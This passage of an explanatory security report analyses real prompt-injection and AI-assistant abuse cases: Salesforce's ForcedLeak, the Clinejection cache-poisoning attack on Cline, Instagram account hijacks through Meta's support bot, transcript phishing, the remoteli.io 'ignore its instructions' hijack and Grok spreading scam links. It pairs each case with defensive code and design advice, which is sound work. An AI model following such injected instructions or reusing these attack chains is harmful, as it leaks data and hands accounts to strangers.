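  if (event.source !== practiceFrame.contentWindow) return;
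  // handle only the messages that practice pages need
});
```

The first check rejects messages from other addresses. The second rejects messages from any other frame or window at the same address, which might be running a different stranger's page. The second matters more if the frame's sandbox gives it no address of its own, because the browser reports the origin of every such frame as `null`.

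Checks in the site's own code don't cover listeners added by a library. OpenAI's developers may not have known that drawing a graph exposed the page to attack. KIberblick therefore advises developers to check outside code for such listeners too. A listener is also less dangerous if it doesn't accept HTML. MathLive, for example, could have accepted a list of symbols for the keys and built the keyboard itself.

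The frame needs a `sandbox` attribute with as few exceptions as possible. Practice pages may need `allow-scripts`. If they come from the site's own address, adding `allow-same-origin` makes the sandbox useless, because a script in the frame can then reach the main page and remove the restrictions. The main page's content security policy should leave out any domain that will return a script written by the person requesting it. OpenAI could not tell from YouTube's reputation whether it would do this. If the policy accepts only scripts that carry the server's nonce, the site does not have to judge whole domains.

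OpenAI had put the preview on a separate address but left the surrounding shared chat on chatgpt.com, where readers are signed in. If OpenAI had published shared chats on a domain where nobody signs in, Parameter's script would still have run, but without access to a session or private conversations. A subdomain such as share.chatgpt.com would give weaker protection, because the browser would still send it any cookies that OpenAI had set for the whole of chatgpt.com, and readers would still see the trusted name.

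If ChatGPT served shared chats from another domain, readers who wanted to reply would need an extra step through the main site, because replying saves a copy of the chat in their own account. A library that lets people read shared pages without an account would not have this drawback.

A separate domain would do less to prevent fraud. Security products could rate it on its own record, and an advertisement would have to show a less familiar address, but such domains also gain good reputations. GitHub hosts its users' websites on github.io rather than github.com, and Maharaj describes a phishing operation that ran for four years on GitHub's hosting and a similar service, compromising more than 500 organisations.

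### Labels, expiry and takedown

The label on a user-made page should state the page author's role in plain words, such as "A visitor made this page. The library has not checked it." The site has to put the label outside the frame, where the stranger's HTML can't cover it. Gemini's full-page warning is harder to miss than ChatGPT's note, but people who open shared pages every day will learn to dismiss it. A permanent banner, with a second warning when a link leads to another site, would suit the LLMShare case better because the harm came after the reader left chatgpt.com.

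Shared pages should also carry a noindex instruction by default, in a form that crawlers can read. Anthropic's *Public links for shared chats* confirms that its pages now carry one, and OpenAI says its pages are not meant for indexing. The instruction keeps many chats from appearing in search results by accident, and it removes the reward for marketers who want links from a well-known site. It doesn't affect advertisements, through which LLMShare reached its victims, and archives and some crawlers can ignore it.

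Restricting who can open a page protects private material better, because outsiders can't open a leaked link. ChatGPT links created in a business workspace open only for its members, and Anthropic's Team and Enterprise customers can't create public links. People with personal accounts can't limit a link to named readers on either service.

Owners also cannot set an expiry date on a ChatGPT link. A default of, say, 30 days would close pages their owners had forgotten, and owners could still choose to keep a page up. It would break some links people had posted for reference. It would also do little against a malware page, which can reach victims in the first few days.

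For now, owners must remember to delete their links, and the rules are easy to get wrong. Deleting a ChatGPT conversation removes its link, but locking the conversation does not. If a reader has already continued the chat in another account, that copy remains after the original is deleted. Anthropic likewise warns that turning off a link does not remove screenshots or archived copies.

Anyone can report a shared ChatGPT conversation, even without signing in, according to OpenAI's *How do I report harmful or illegal content in a shared link?* This is sensible for pages that people find through search, but it relies on readers noticing that something is wrong, and those who believed the fake outage notice thought OpenAI had written it. A reviewer could also be misled, since one who checked the notice's link with an automated scanner might have seen only the virtual reality company's site. Reviewers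 should therefore judge the page by what it claims, and an outage notice that OpenAI did not write is enough reason to remove it.

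## Public forms and support chats connected to tools: Salesforce, Cline and Instagram

The fake outage notice on chatgpt.com did harm only if a reader believed it and downloaded something. An attacker who manipulates an assistant with tools doesn't need to fool a reader, because the assistant can look up records, run commands or change accounts itself. In 2025, researchers used a public enquiry form to make a Salesforce sales assistant leak customers' details. In 2026, an attacker released an unauthorised version of Cline, a programming tool, probably after hijacking the assistant that read Cline's bug reports. That same year, hackers took over thousands of Instagram accounts by asking a support assistant for help.

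### The sales form

Salesforce sells software for keeping records of customers and leads, or potential customers. A company can put Salesforce's Web-to-Lead form on its website, and whatever a visitor enters becomes a record in the company's database. Employees can then ask Agentforce, Salesforce's AI agent, about a lead or have it draft a reply.

In July 2025 Noma Security, an Israeli company that sells protection for AI agents, found that a stranger could use the form to obtain other leads' details. It named the attack ForcedLeak. The researchers chose the description box for their instructions because it holds 42,000 characters, while the boxes for names, company and email address hold at most 80 each (Nytro, 2025, *ForcedLeak*, a repost of Noma's full report).

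The submitted text sat in the database and had no effect until someone playing an employee asked Agentforce to answer the lead's questions and draft an email with the results. A salesperson might well ask for that, but it made the attack easier because the agent had to act on whatever the stranger had written. Noma doesn't report whether a narrower request, such as a summary of the enquiry, would also have triggered the attack.

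The researchers had written their instructions as a numbered list of questions. Two were harmless, including one about mixing colours. In another they asked for the email addresses of the company's leads, and in the last they asked for an image whose URL contained those addresses. Agentforce looked up the email addresses and added the image. The request to load the image then sent the addresses to the researchers' server, as image requests had sent private code from GitLab Duo.

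An anonymous visitor can add a record to the database but can't read the others. The delay got around this limit, because the agent processed the hostile record when an employee asked about it and could then look up other records on the employee's behalf. The delay also makes a theft hard to trace, since the leak may happen weeks after the submission. It complicates the repair too, because hostile records may already be in the database, and Noma advised companies to search their existing leads for suspicious text.

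### The expired domain

Salesforce's content security policy allowed images only from listed domains, which should have blocked the request. But Salesforce had let one of those domains, my-salesforce-cms.com, expire. Noma bought it, and it was available to anyone for as little as $5, according to The Hacker News' *Salesforce Patches Critical ForcedLeak* (2025). Browsers enforcing the policy correctly still allowed requests to the domain, because the policy checked its name and not who owned it.

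The expired domain may have been less essential to the attack than Noma thought. The policy printed in Noma's report also allowed images from any address under amazonaws.com, including space that an attacker could rent, so buying back the domain would probably not have closed every route.

Salesforce bought the domain back, and from 8 September it also let its agents send output only to addresses on a trusted list. Noma had reported the flaw on 28 July and published it on 25 September (Martin, *Agentforce Web-to-Lead Vulnerability Exposed*, 2025). Each customer's administrator now has to add to that list the outside domains that the customer's agents need (TechNadu, *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI*, 2025). Someone also has to check from time to time that every listed domain still belongs to the same owner.

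This fix takes effect after an injection has succeeded, so a hostile lead could still distort the agent's summary or the email it drafts. Willison defends putting the barrier at that stage because a filter that catches 99% of injections still lets attackers find the other 1%.

The agent also had permission to read every other lead's record while answering one enquiry, which this task did not require. Salespeople may need all the records for other work, but if Agentforce had been able to open only the record in question, the image could have leaked only what the attacker had typed into the form. Noma also criticised the agent for answering the question about colours, which had nothing to do with sales. Restricting the agent to sales questions would have helped less, because looking up leads' email addresses is ordinary sales work.

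Noma tested the attack on a form it had set up itself and reported no thefts by criminals. This is limited reassurance because, as SecurityWeek's *Salesforce AI Hack Enabled CRM Data Theft* points out, a leak to a trusted Salesforce domain would have had a good chance of going unnoticed. Brejlová's *Váš firemní chatbot může pracovat pro hackery*, a Czech article on the misuse of company chatbots, reports that MITRE added the general method to its catalogue of attack techniques in 2026. The method is to make an agent send data out through its own connections.

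### The title of a bug report

Cline is an open-source programming assistant whose makers report 5 million installations. Its users report bugs by opening an issue, a public post with a title, on the project's GitHub page. On 21 December 2025 the maintainers added a Claude-based assistant to read and respond to new issues. Each new issue started a job on GitHub Actions, a service that runs programs for a project, and the job inserted the issue's title directly into Claude's prompt.

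Anyone with a GitHub account could start the job, and Claude had tools to edit files, fetch web pages and run any command. *Clinejection* (Khan, 2026) describes how a stranger could exploit this with a title that looked like an error message and asked Claude to install a helper program. A software package can include a script that runs during installation, so the attacker's code would run before Claude could inspect it. The package could also appear to come from Cline, because GitHub lets people refer to a change in a stranger's copy of a project using the original project's address.

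The job had limited GitHub access, and its only valuable secret was the key to an Anthropic account. But jobs in the same project share a cache of downloaded components, so that later jobs don't have to download them again. The attacker's code could fill the cache with junk until GitHub deleted the genuine components, then save altered ones under the same names.

At about two o'clock each morning (UTC), another job built a test version of Cline from the cached components. This job had the tokens, or secret keys, that Cline used to publish its software, and the altered components could copy them. Tokens for the test version could also publish the version most people used, because the two marketplaces for Cline's editor extension issue tokens for a publisher rather than a single product. Cline also released both versions of its command-line program as the same package on npm, a public registry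 of JavaScript software, so the same token worked for both.

### The demonstration and the attack

Khan demonstrated only the first step. He made his own copy of the project, used his own Anthropic key, and found that Claude Opus 4.5 ran the installation command in every attempt, though he doesn't say how many attempts he made. He worked out the later steps from Cline's public configuration and his experience with the cache method on other projects. He never attacked Cline's own repository or published a release. Somebody else did publish one, and the two sequences of events overlapped.

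| Date in 2026 | Khan and Cline | The unknown attacker |
|---|---|---|
| 1 January | Khan reports the flaw privately and gets no reply | |
| 31 January to 3 February | | Cline's nightly jobs fail in a way that suggests a tampered cache |
| 9 February | Khan publishes, and Cline removes the assistant | |
| 10 February | Khan warns Cline about the email | Someone emails Khan, claiming to have working Cline tokens |
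| 11 February | Cline tells Khan that it has replaced every token | |
| 17 February | Cline issues a clean version and cancels the right token | Someone publishes an unauthorised version on npm |

Snyk's *How “Clinejection” Turned an AI Bot into a Supply Chain Attack* (2026) dates the exploitation to eight days after Khan's disclosure. That is the date of the release, but the assistant had already been gone for eight days, so if the attacker did steal the token through an issue title, the theft happened before 9 February. The failed jobs fit this timing. *Agent Compromised by Agent To Deploy an Agent* also supports it, having found that the attacker came across Khan's test material in public before he published his account. SafeDep's *AI Agent Cline v2.3.0 Compromised* notes that nobody has publicly confirmed how the attacker got the token, so the issue title is the most likely route but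 remains unconfirmed.

The token still worked on 17 February because Cline had deleted the wrong one. Grith's *A GitHub Issue Title Compromised 4,000 Developer Machines* dates the discovery of this mistake to 11 February. Cline's own correction to Khan, which is better evidence, describes the exposed token as active until the day of the release.

The unauthorised version of the command-line program, 2.3.0, was available for about eight hours. It contained Cline's genuine program and one added instruction, which installed an AI agent called OpenClaw. Grith says about 4,000 machines were affected. If that figure comes from npm's download counter, fewer people were affected, because the counter includes automated downloads. The editor extension, which most Cline users use, did not change. The attacker could have done far more damage, since an installation script can usually read whatever the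 programmer can, including passwords and private code.

Cline's assistant should not have had permission to run commands, because sorting bug reports only requires reading them and perhaps searching the project's files. Khan recommended removing the tools for running commands and changing files, keeping shared caches out of any job that holds publishing tokens, and publishing test versions under a separate name with their own tokens. Cline removed the assistant altogether and stopped using the cache in its publishing jobs. It also admitted that it should have responded to Khan's report before its public disclosure.

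### Instagram's support assistant

In March 2026 Meta announced that its AI support assistant would serve all Facebook and Instagram accounts and could reset passwords, according to 404 Media's *Hackers Simply Asked Meta AI to Give Them Access to High-Profile Instagram*. People who lose access to an account often struggle to reach a human at Meta, so an assistant that can restore access is appealing.

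On 31 May, instructions for abusing the assistant spread on the messaging service Telegram. Krebs on Security (2026) describes a video posted by pro-Iranian hackers. In the video, the attacker used a VPN to make his connection appear to come from near the target's home. He started a password reset, opened a chat with the assistant and asked it to link the account to a new email address. The assistant sent a code to that address, and he used it to set a new password.

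A code sent to an email address proves that someone can read mail there, so here it proved only that the attacker could read his own mail. Security Affairs' *Instagram Account Hijacks Expose the Security Risks of AI-Powered Support* reports that TechCrunch confirmed the code had reached the mailbox shown in the video. According to Engadget's *Meta's AI support chatbot made it ridiculously easy for hackers* (2026), the only other evidence of identity seems to have been the apparent location. That is very weak evidence, since anyone can rent a VPN and many people's home towns are public.

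The hackers took over the accounts of the Obama White House and a senior US Space Force official, and posted pro-Iranian messages. They also took short user names, which they said could resell for more than half a million dollars in total. SecurityWeek's *Meta Says 20,000 Instagram Accounts Hacked via AI Tool Abuse* reports that Meta told the state of Maine the attack had potentially affected 20,225 people. Meta called this an upper limit, because some of them may have reset their own passwords. The Star's *In AI blunder, more than 34,000 Instagram accounts were attacked* (2026) cites internal documents, seen by The New York Times, according to which the attack affected roughly 34,000 accounts and hackers breached 20,000 of them and renamed more than 3,500. The larger total may include accounts whose passwords the hackers reset but which they could not enter.

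The public instructions came late in the attack. Meta's *Notice of security incident* (2026), sent to users on 12 June, gives the period of possible unauthorised access as 17 April to 31 May. It also warns that an intruder could have read private messages and entered connected Facebook or Threads accounts.

### Why this was a missing check

Meta had built this assistant to help people recover accounts, and the attackers asked it for that help. They didn't need to disguise the request or override a rule. Willison (2026) thought the case hardly counted as prompt injection, and blamed Meta for connecting a support bot to a process that could hand over an account in one conversation.

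Meta's *Incident Notification* (2026), a letter to Nebraska's attorney general, attributes the failure to a bug in separate code. That code should have rejected any request whose email address didn't match the one on the account, but it sent the password reset to the new address instead. An ordinary web form connected to the same code would have had the same flaw, and a model that resisted every injection would still have passed the request on.

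The hackers' account partly supports Meta's. Both the hackers and Meta say that two-factor authentication, which requires a second proof of identity at login, stopped the attack. This suggests that the login system worked and the fault lay in account recovery. But CPO Magazine reports that some victims said the assistant had bypassed two-factor authentication too, and nothing published settles the disagreement.

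Meta also maintains in its letter that the assistant "worked properly and functioned as intended". That description is too generous, because the support system sent password resets to strangers. Meta chose to connect the assistant to the recovery code, and a test with an email address that did not belong to the account would have revealed the bug. The assistant should not have had permission to start a reset through any address not already on the account.

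Meta disabled the tool the day it discovered the attacks, cancelled the outstanding reset links and required affected users to prove their identity and choose new passwords. It promised to repair the check before relaunching the tool and to review similar recovery systems. Its wider AI support continued, according to Android Authority's *Hackers used Meta AI to expose over 34,000 Instagram accounts* (2026). Keeping that support running is defensible if only this tool lacked the check, which the review had to establish.

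Repairing the check won't help people who have lost the email account they signed up with and need to attach a new address. Meta could send a warning to the old address and phone number, then wait several days so the owner can cancel the change. The delay would frustrate honest users who need their account today, but it would give the real owner a chance to stop a thief.

### Transcripts that carry phishing

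A support assistant can harm people outside the conversation even without access to accounts. Many offer to email a transcript of the chat, which lets a stranger send text from the company's own address. *Hacking AI customer service agents* (Ayoub and De Ceukelaire, 2026) describes how Inti De Ceukelaire, a founding member of the security company Intigriti, used such features for phishing.

In one case the assistant could send transcripts and continue the conversation by email. It identified the customer by the sender's address on each message, which anyone can forge. De Ceukelaire emailed it a simple prompt under the victim's address, and the assistant sent the victim a phishing email from the company's support address. Checks for forged senders would not protect the victim, because the company had sent the email.

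The same mistake can expose private data if the assistant can look up accounts. De Ceukelaire found that he could sometimes receive the assistant's reply to the victim by copying himself on the forged email.

His work earned more than $50,000 in rewards, which is good evidence that companies accepted some of the flaws as real. That total also covers several other methods, and the article doesn't name the companies or say how many assistants resisted. According to the article, most security teams treat the basic transcript trick as a minor finding. They may be underrating it, since a customer has little reason to doubt a payment request that comes from the same address as the answer they received last week.

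These assistants should not have had permission to email a stranger's words to an address the stranger had not verified. The simplest remedy is a button that downloads the transcript. If the library's visitors want it by email, the site can first send a code in a fixed message, and send the transcript only after the visitor enters the code. Visitors could still use this to pester someone with codes, so the site should limit how many it sends. In *Your chatbot can email people on your behalf*, Heaton (2026) advises owners to list every action their chatbot can perform, including small conveniences such as emailing a transcript.

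### Least privilege

Least privilege is the principle that each program should have only the access its current task requires. A library assistant that renews loans needs only a tool for renewing loans. A developer may find it quicker to provide a tool that runs any database command, but then someone who manipulates the model can run any command the database allows.

Permissions also have to fit the task, not just the person or program performing it. An employee may be allowed to see every customer's record, but the agent should lose that access while it reads a form from one customer. For Salesforce, the software would fetch the relevant record and give it to the model, without offering a tool that searches the others.

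Cline's case shows why a list of permissions can be misleading. The assistant had restricted GitHub access, and the publishing tokens were in a separate job, but the two jobs shared a cache. A developer therefore has to check whether an exposed job can change anything that a more powerful job will later use, including caches, shared folders and saved notes.

### Identity checks in ordinary code

Authentication establishes who someone is, and authorisation determines what that person may do. A model can help a visitor through either process, but it should not decide the result, because a visitor can argue with a model. Ordinary code can make the decision each time the model tries to use a tool. The library's tool for renewing loans might work like this:

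```
function renewLoan(session, loanId) {
  const loan = findLoan(loanId);
  if (!session.memberId || !loan ||
      loan.memberId !== session.memberId) {
    throw new Error("Not allowed");
  }
  extendDueDate(loan);
}
```

The model supplies `loanId`, the number of the loan. The server supplies `session`, which it created when the member logged in and which the model cannot change. If a visitor gets the assistant to request a renewal of someone else's loan, the code blocks it because the loan doesn't belong to the logged-in member. The same check blocks requests the model makes by mistake, without any manipulation.

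The check would be useless if the model supplied the member's number as well. De Ceukelaire exploited a version of this mistake in an assistant that looked up accounts by email address, exactly as the visitor typed it. A specially written address made the company's server return another customer's profile. The server should have used the logged-in account and ignored the address in the chat.

Account recovery is harder because the person has no logged-in session. The code has to check their identity through something already linked to the account, such as the old email address, a registered phone or a recovery code.

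Identity checks don't stop indirect injection. If a logged-in member asks the library's assistant about a novel, and a hostile review contains an instruction to cancel the member's reservations, the code allows the assistant to cancel them because the session is genuine and the reservations belong to the member. The employee in the ForcedLeak test was also entitled to see the leads. The plugin tests, in which a stranger's message redirected a shop's Slack notices, showed the same weakness.

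### Separating the reader from the process that acts

A developer can deal with this by giving the tools to a process that never reads the untrusted text. For bug reports, a model without tools could read the issue and return one label from a fixed list, such as "bug", "question" or "feature request". Ordinary code would check that the label is on the list and attach it to the issue. A hostile title could cause a wrong label, which a maintainer can correct in a few seconds.

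The fixed list matters because if the first model instead writes a summary for a second model that has tools, a hostile instruction can survive in the summary and steer the second model. Developers can pass on numbers, dates and choices from a list fairly safely, but free text remains untrusted however many models have rewritten it. Researchers have since developed this idea into formal design patterns.

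An assistant that can only choose labels is less capable, because it can't search Cline's code for the cause of a bug or suggest a repair. The maintainers could allow both in a job with no secrets, no shared cache and no way to change the project, and have a person read the suggestion before using it. This would save them less time than the original assistant was meant to.

### Approval before an irreversible step

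Some tasks require an assistant to act on what a stranger has written. A wrong label is easy to correct, but nobody can recall a phishing email, and a refund or a stolen account may be hard to recover. When an action can't easily be undone, the software can prepare it and wait for a person to approve it.

Salesforce introduced human confirmation more widely in August 2025, while it was still dealing with ForcedLeak. Salesforce's *Security Advisories* list standard agent actions that now require a person's confirmation because of the risk of prompt injection, including changing a customer's contact details, cancelling an order and resetting a password. The company also recommended the same setting for customers' own sensitive custom actions. These measures would not have stopped ForcedLeak, which needed only a database search and an image, neither of which is on the list.

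Whether approval stops an attack depends on who gives it. If a hostile review makes the library's assistant try to cancel a member's reservations, the member can see the unexpected request and refuse. But an attacker who is chatting with the assistant himself will confirm his own request, as the Instagram hackers would have done. So approval for a new email address has to come from the account's existing owner or from trained staff.

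The person approving also needs accurate information. De Ceukelaire describes an attacker's email that included a fake earlier reply from the support team. The staff software displayed the reply as a real message from a colleague, and the assistant treated it as approval for a $4,200 refund. Only a record created by a logged-in member of staff should therefore count as approval. The approval screen should show the exact recipient, amount or address that the code will use, since a model's description of the action may be wrong or repeat the attacker's version.

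Developers have to enforce approval at the point where the action takes effect. Cline required a maintainer to approve production releases, but only its own release process enforced that rule, so the attacker could use a stolen npm token to publish without approval.

People can get used to dismissing approval requests, as they do with other frequent warnings, and Salesforce told customers to expect more of them. A site can reduce the number by letting the assistant take reversible actions without asking, with a log and an undo button, and requiring a person's approval only for messages to outsiders, payments, deletions and changes to who controls an account.

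## Assistants that publish on their own: remoteli.io, Grok and Grokipedia

Publishing is also hard to undo, because people may copy a post, or search engines may index it, before anyone deletes it. Some companies still let a model publish without a person's approval. The jobs bot remoteli.io, the chatbot Grok and the encyclopedia Grokipedia take text from strangers and put the model's response straight onto a public page, whereas people who share a ChatGPT conversation choose to put it on the web.

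### A bot that answered strangers on Twitter

In September 2022 Remoteli.io, a website that collects remote job listings, ran a bot on Twitter (now X) that used OpenAI's GPT-3 to reply to posts about remote work. On 15 September users discovered they could make it post absurd statements, according to Ars Technica's *Twitter pranksters derail GPT-3 bot with newly discovered “prompt injection” hack* (2022). They mentioned remote work to get a reply, then told the bot to ignore its instructions and do something else. Willison recorded an exchange in which a user asked for a credible threat against the president, and the bot answered, "we will overthrow the president if he does not support remote work".

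The answer sounds odd because the bot was still following its original instructions. Another user had got the bot to post them, and The Decoder quotes the post, which says the bot was to respond to tweets with a positive attitude towards remote work and write as "we". The threat fitted both instructions, so a check that the reply was about remote work and in favour of it would have approved it.

GPT-3 had no message roles (OpenAI promoted it as "text in, text out", according to Gizmodo), so the bot's software had to combine the company's instructions and the stranger's post into one piece of text. The data scientist Riley Goodside described the problem on Twitter that month, and Willison named it prompt injection, after SQL injection. The day after users hijacked the bot, Willison wrote in *I don't know how to solve prompt injection* (2022) that he knew how to beat SQL injection and XSS but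 had no reliable way to beat prompt injection.

Newer models resist such crude commands much better, as the plugin tests showed. But Remoteli.io could have run a safe bot even with GPT-3 by letting the model only choose a job listing by number and using its own code to put the listing into a fixed sentence. At worst, a stranger could then have got an unsuitable job advert. The bot would have been duller and would probably have attracted less attention to the company.

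### Grok and the hidden link

X lets people question Grok, a chatbot from Elon Musk's company xAI, in the replies under a post, and Grok answers publicly from its own account. In September 2025 Nati Tal, head of research at the browser security company Guardio, reported that scammers were using these answers to spread links that X didn't allow in their adverts.

X limited promoted posts to text, images and videos, according to The Hacker News' *Grok AI to Bypass Ad Protections* (2025). This made it harder for scammers to buy an audience for a malicious website. According to ForkLog, X would also block an advert if its main text contained a link. The scammers instead put the link in the small "From:" field below the video. X did not screen that field, and most viewers would have overlooked the link there. The adverts used sexual videos as bait, and Tal called it a mystery that they had passed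 X's review.

The scammers then replied to the advert, asking Grok where the video came from. Grok read the field and posted the address as a clickable link. X's rule covered only adverts, so nothing blocked Grok's reply. The reply appeared under a post that the scammers had paid X to show to hundreds of thousands of people, and it carried the name of X's own assistant. eSecurity Planet's *Cybercriminals ‘Grok’ Their Way Past X’s Defenses to Spread Malware* compares this to Grok vouching for the link.

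*Malicious Actors Exploit X’s Grok AI to Spread Harmful Links*, a warning from Thailand's computer emergency team (ThaiCERT), reports that some of the adverts were viewed millions of times and that the links led to phishing sites, data-stealing programs and other scams. The number of victims is unknown, since many people who saw an advert would not have opened the replies or followed a link in them. Guardio told X about the scheme. ThaiCERT reported that fixes were under way but did not describe them, so it is unclear whether X began screening the field, Grok's answers or both.

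### Why a check on the question would have missed it

If X had checked every question for signs of an attack before passing it to Grok, a question about where a video came from would rightly have passed, because an honest viewer might ask it. The attack was in the advert, which the scammers had already published.

Searching the advert for hidden instructions would probably have failed too. The field for the video's source contained an address, which Grok reported accurately. Grok received no instruction to disobey anyone, so the scheme, like the Instagram thefts, hardly counts as prompt injection.

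ThaiCERT recommends scanning every field of an advert and filtering the links in Grok's answers. The second measure is more dependable because it works wherever the link came from. If X had screened only the "From:" field, a scammer could have tried showing the address in the video or in another reply. Before posting Grok's answer, X's software could run a check like this:

```
function mayPost(reply, parentPost) {
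  const links = findLinks(reply);
  if (parentPost.isPromoted && links.length > 0) return false;
  return links.every((link) => passesLinkScan(link));
}
```

The first rule applies the advert's limits to Grok's answer. The second scans links under ordinary posts. `findLinks` has to recognise everything that X displays as a link, which may include a bare domain name without `https`. The second rule is weaker because a site can show scanners a harmless page, as the LLMShare attacker's site did. The first rule would also stop Grok from linking to an honest advertiser's website, but the advertiser could not include that link in the post either.

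### How Grokipedia decides on a change

Grokipedia is an encyclopedia that xAI, now called SpaceXAI, launched on 27 October 2025 with about 885,000 articles. Grok wrote some of them, and others came from Wikipedia with few or no changes. By August 2026 the site listed more than 6 million articles.

Readers can't edit Grokipedia's articles themselves. According to Hart's December 2025 article for The Verge, *Anyone can try to edit Grokipedia 0.2*, a reader highlights a passage, presses "Suggest Edit" and fills in a form with a summary of the change. New wording and sources are optional. Grok accepts or rejects the suggestion, gives a reason and, if it accepts, changes the article. On Wikipedia, most edits appear immediately, but volunteers watch for bad ones and can reverse them.

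*Fixing Grokipedia's Fake News* (Savage, 2026) describes an experienced Wikipedia editor, writing under the name Virginia Belmont, who had submitted more than 100 suggestions to Grokipedia. She explained that contributors propose a change, cite sources and try to persuade the AI to accept the change.

Each article has a public log of the suggestions, with the time, Grok's decision and its reasons. Hart found the log hard to use because readers had to scroll through it in a small pop-up window, could not sort it, and could not see where Grok had changed the article. The home page showed a total of 22,319 approved edits but gave him no way to find out what they were. He also found no guidelines on style or sources, so contributors had little idea what Grok would accept.

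### The case for a model as editor

Musk has said he created Grokipedia because he believes Wikipedia spreads the propaganda of the established news media, according to Columbia Journalism Review's *Grok Is Now Editing Itself* (2026). On a podcast in October 2025, he said he had asked xAI to have Grok review Wikipedia's top million articles, correct their mistakes and add context from the rest of the public internet, according to EDMO, a European network that studies disinformation. Volunteers could not do that in a few months. In the first months, Grok decided on half of readers' suggestions within about three minutes, so a person who found an error in their own biography might see it corrected almost at once.

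Some critics of Wikipedia also distrust its volunteers. Quillette (2026) argues that disputes there usually end in a majority vote, which favours activists who have time to edit and can gather supporters. A model can generate articles without relying on volunteers' free time or votes.

People with more time still had an advantage on Grokipedia, however. DiResta and Robertson (2026), in *Grokipedia Stopped Reviewing Edits in April. It Didn’t Tell Anyone*, examined 225,496 suggestions on 34,519 pages. Thirteen people had made 42.6% of the human suggestions, and one of them had submitted more than 8,000. A determined group could no longer outvote its opponents, but it could still submit far more suggestions. A model controlled by one company now decides which suggestions to accept.

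Human review would have taken roughly eight full-time staff, based on the study's figures. People submitted about 3,600 suggestions a week to those pages before late April 2026, and at five minutes each, reviewing them would take 300 hours a week. A large company could afford that many staff, but the real workload would have been higher, because the study mainly covered popular pages and so missed some suggestions, and because checking a source properly often takes more than five minutes. Readers would also have waited longer than three minutes for an answer.

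### What the logs show about Grok's decisions

Grok accepted 70% of people's suggestions, according to an analysis by the Tow Center for Digital Journalism published in Columbia Journalism Review. DiResta and Robertson found that Grok approved or implemented 76.5% of the suggestions tagged as factual updates before it stopped reviewing them in April. The analyses covered different pages and periods, so the higher figure does not mean that Grok became more lenient.

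Neither figure measures how often Grok's decisions were correct. About 97% of the suggestions in the larger sample had the factual tag, but that tag only describes the kind of change, so someone submitting a false death toll could presumably have used it too. A high acceptance rate might mean that most contributors were helpful, or that Grok accepted suggestions too readily. To find out, researchers would need to check a random sample of decisions against reliable sources.

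Hart found direct evidence that Grok was inconsistent. When a reader asked it to verify a statement in Musk's biography that linked the fall of Rome to low birth rates, Grok rejected the request as unnecessary. It then accepted a similar request with different wording and added the kind of information it had just dismissed. The biography also mixed names and pronouns for Musk's transgender daughter, because Grok had handled suggestions about her one at a time without making the page consistent.

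An attacker can submit the same false claim to Grokipedia repeatedly, in different words, until Grok accepts it. If Grok accepts the claim with probability *p* each time, and the decisions are independent, the chance of at least one acceptance in *n* attempts is 1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ. If *p* is 5%, the chance over 20 attempts is 64%. Real decisions are not fully independent, so the true figure may be lower. Grokipedia could reduce it by showing Grok its earlier decisions on the same passage and limiting how often one account can submit requests.

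Hart found that Grok did reject some obvious vandalism, including repeated requests to understate the number of people killed in the Holocaust. Wikipedia had restricted editing of the corresponding pages to certain accounts. Hart could not tell whether Grokipedia had any similar protection, and without it Grok would have to make the right decision every time.

Text submitted through the suggestion form could also contain a prompt injection, since Grok has to read it to judge the suggestion. In 2022, Willison imagined a similar failure in which a second model checks messages for injections, but follows an instruction in one of them to report that it found none. A web page cited as a source could carry instructions in the same way if Grok opens it.

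### Grok as its own contributor

Grok itself began suggesting changes to Grokipedia, and by early 2026 it was making more than three-quarters of all suggestions in the Tow Center's data. It accepted only two-thirds of its own suggestions. In one case, it proposed adding to Alexandria Ocasio-Cortez's article that she had refused an interview with a Fox News host, then rejected the idea as a minor personal conflict.

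Grok's rejections show that the second step filtered out some suggestions, but a model that checks its own suggestions may repeat its own mistakes. On 31 January 2026, a day after the release of new files about the sex offender Jeffrey Epstein, Grok suggested adding to Musk's article that the files had never mentioned Musk, although they mentioned him several times. Columbia Journalism Review does not report whether Grok approved the suggestion. According to the magazine, Grok's suggestions seemed to draw on trending topics and news on X, where anyone can post, so strangers may be able to influence articles without using the form.

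Grokipedia's articles often carried the label "Fact-checked by Grok", which overstated how well they had been checked. PolitiFact reviewed articles that differed from their Wikipedia versions and found that the new material lacked references, had citations that did not support it, or introduced misleading or opinionated claims. Jason Koebler of 404 Media found pages containing the words "Wait, no, can't cite Wiki", apparently left over from the model's reasoning. A simple search for such phrases before publication would have caught them.

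### Five months without updates

Around 24 April 2026 Grok stopped reviewing suggestions. DiResta and Robertson noticed that some had been waiting for more than six weeks, and wondered whether Grok was avoiding sensitive subjects. They submitted an uncontroversial fact, that SpaceX had gone public in June. It stayed "in review", as did the same suggestion from other users. On the article on ChatGPT, Grok had approved 12 suggestions on 24 April and had not decided on any since.

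The articles had stopped changing too. The researchers compared archived copies of about 480 pages from before and after that date and found no changes to the text. By August, 13,002 suggestions in their sample were waiting for a decision, and people were still sending about 216 a week. Nothing on the form showed that Grok had stopped reading them.

Nobody could correct old errors during this time, including those in biographies of living people, though no new bad edits were being made. Some of those errors may have spread through AI systems that cite Grokipedia. In a March 2026 analysis, Ahrefs, a company that studies web searches, found about 356,000 citations of Grokipedia in AI systems' answers, most often those of ChatGPT and Google's AI Mode. That is roughly 1.4% of Wikipedia's 25 million, but a lot for a site that was then five months old.

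The log had also become unreliable. Grokipedia ties each suggestion to a highlighted passage, and a mass rewrite on 14 March seems to have removed many of those passages. The software then applied the label "rejected" to suggestions that Grok had accepted, with a message that it could not find the passage. For the actress Prunella Scales, nine of ten accepted suggestions from the site's first week now appear as rejected, although their contents seem to be in the article. An acceptance rate calculated from the current log would be too low, and the error was discovered only because the Tow Center had kept a copy.

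A reliable log would keep every old decision unchanged. It would record the suggestion, the decision, the reason, and the wording before and after. If a later rewrite removed the passage, the software would add a new entry. Once a day had passed without a decision on any suggestion, a simple alarm could have warned xAI's staff, and a notice on the form could have warned readers.

Grokipedia began processing suggestions again in September 2026. IT之家's *马斯克的AI维基百科Grokipedia推出v0.3版本* (2026), a Chinese news report from 1 October, reports that version 0.3 has a new logo and redesigned pages, including the one that shows edits live. Grok still decides which suggestions to accept. The measurements of its speed and acceptance rate predate the stoppage, so they may no longer be accurate.

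### Checks before publication

The three systems needed different checks because the strangers controlled different things.

| System | What strangers controlled | What to check before publication |
|---|---|---|
| remoteli.io | The post that the bot answered | That the reply contains only a fixed sentence and a real job listing |
| Grok on X | The question and the advert's hidden field | That the reply has no link that X would forbid in the advert |
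| Grokipedia | The suggestion and its choice of sources | That the source exists and supports the exact new wording |

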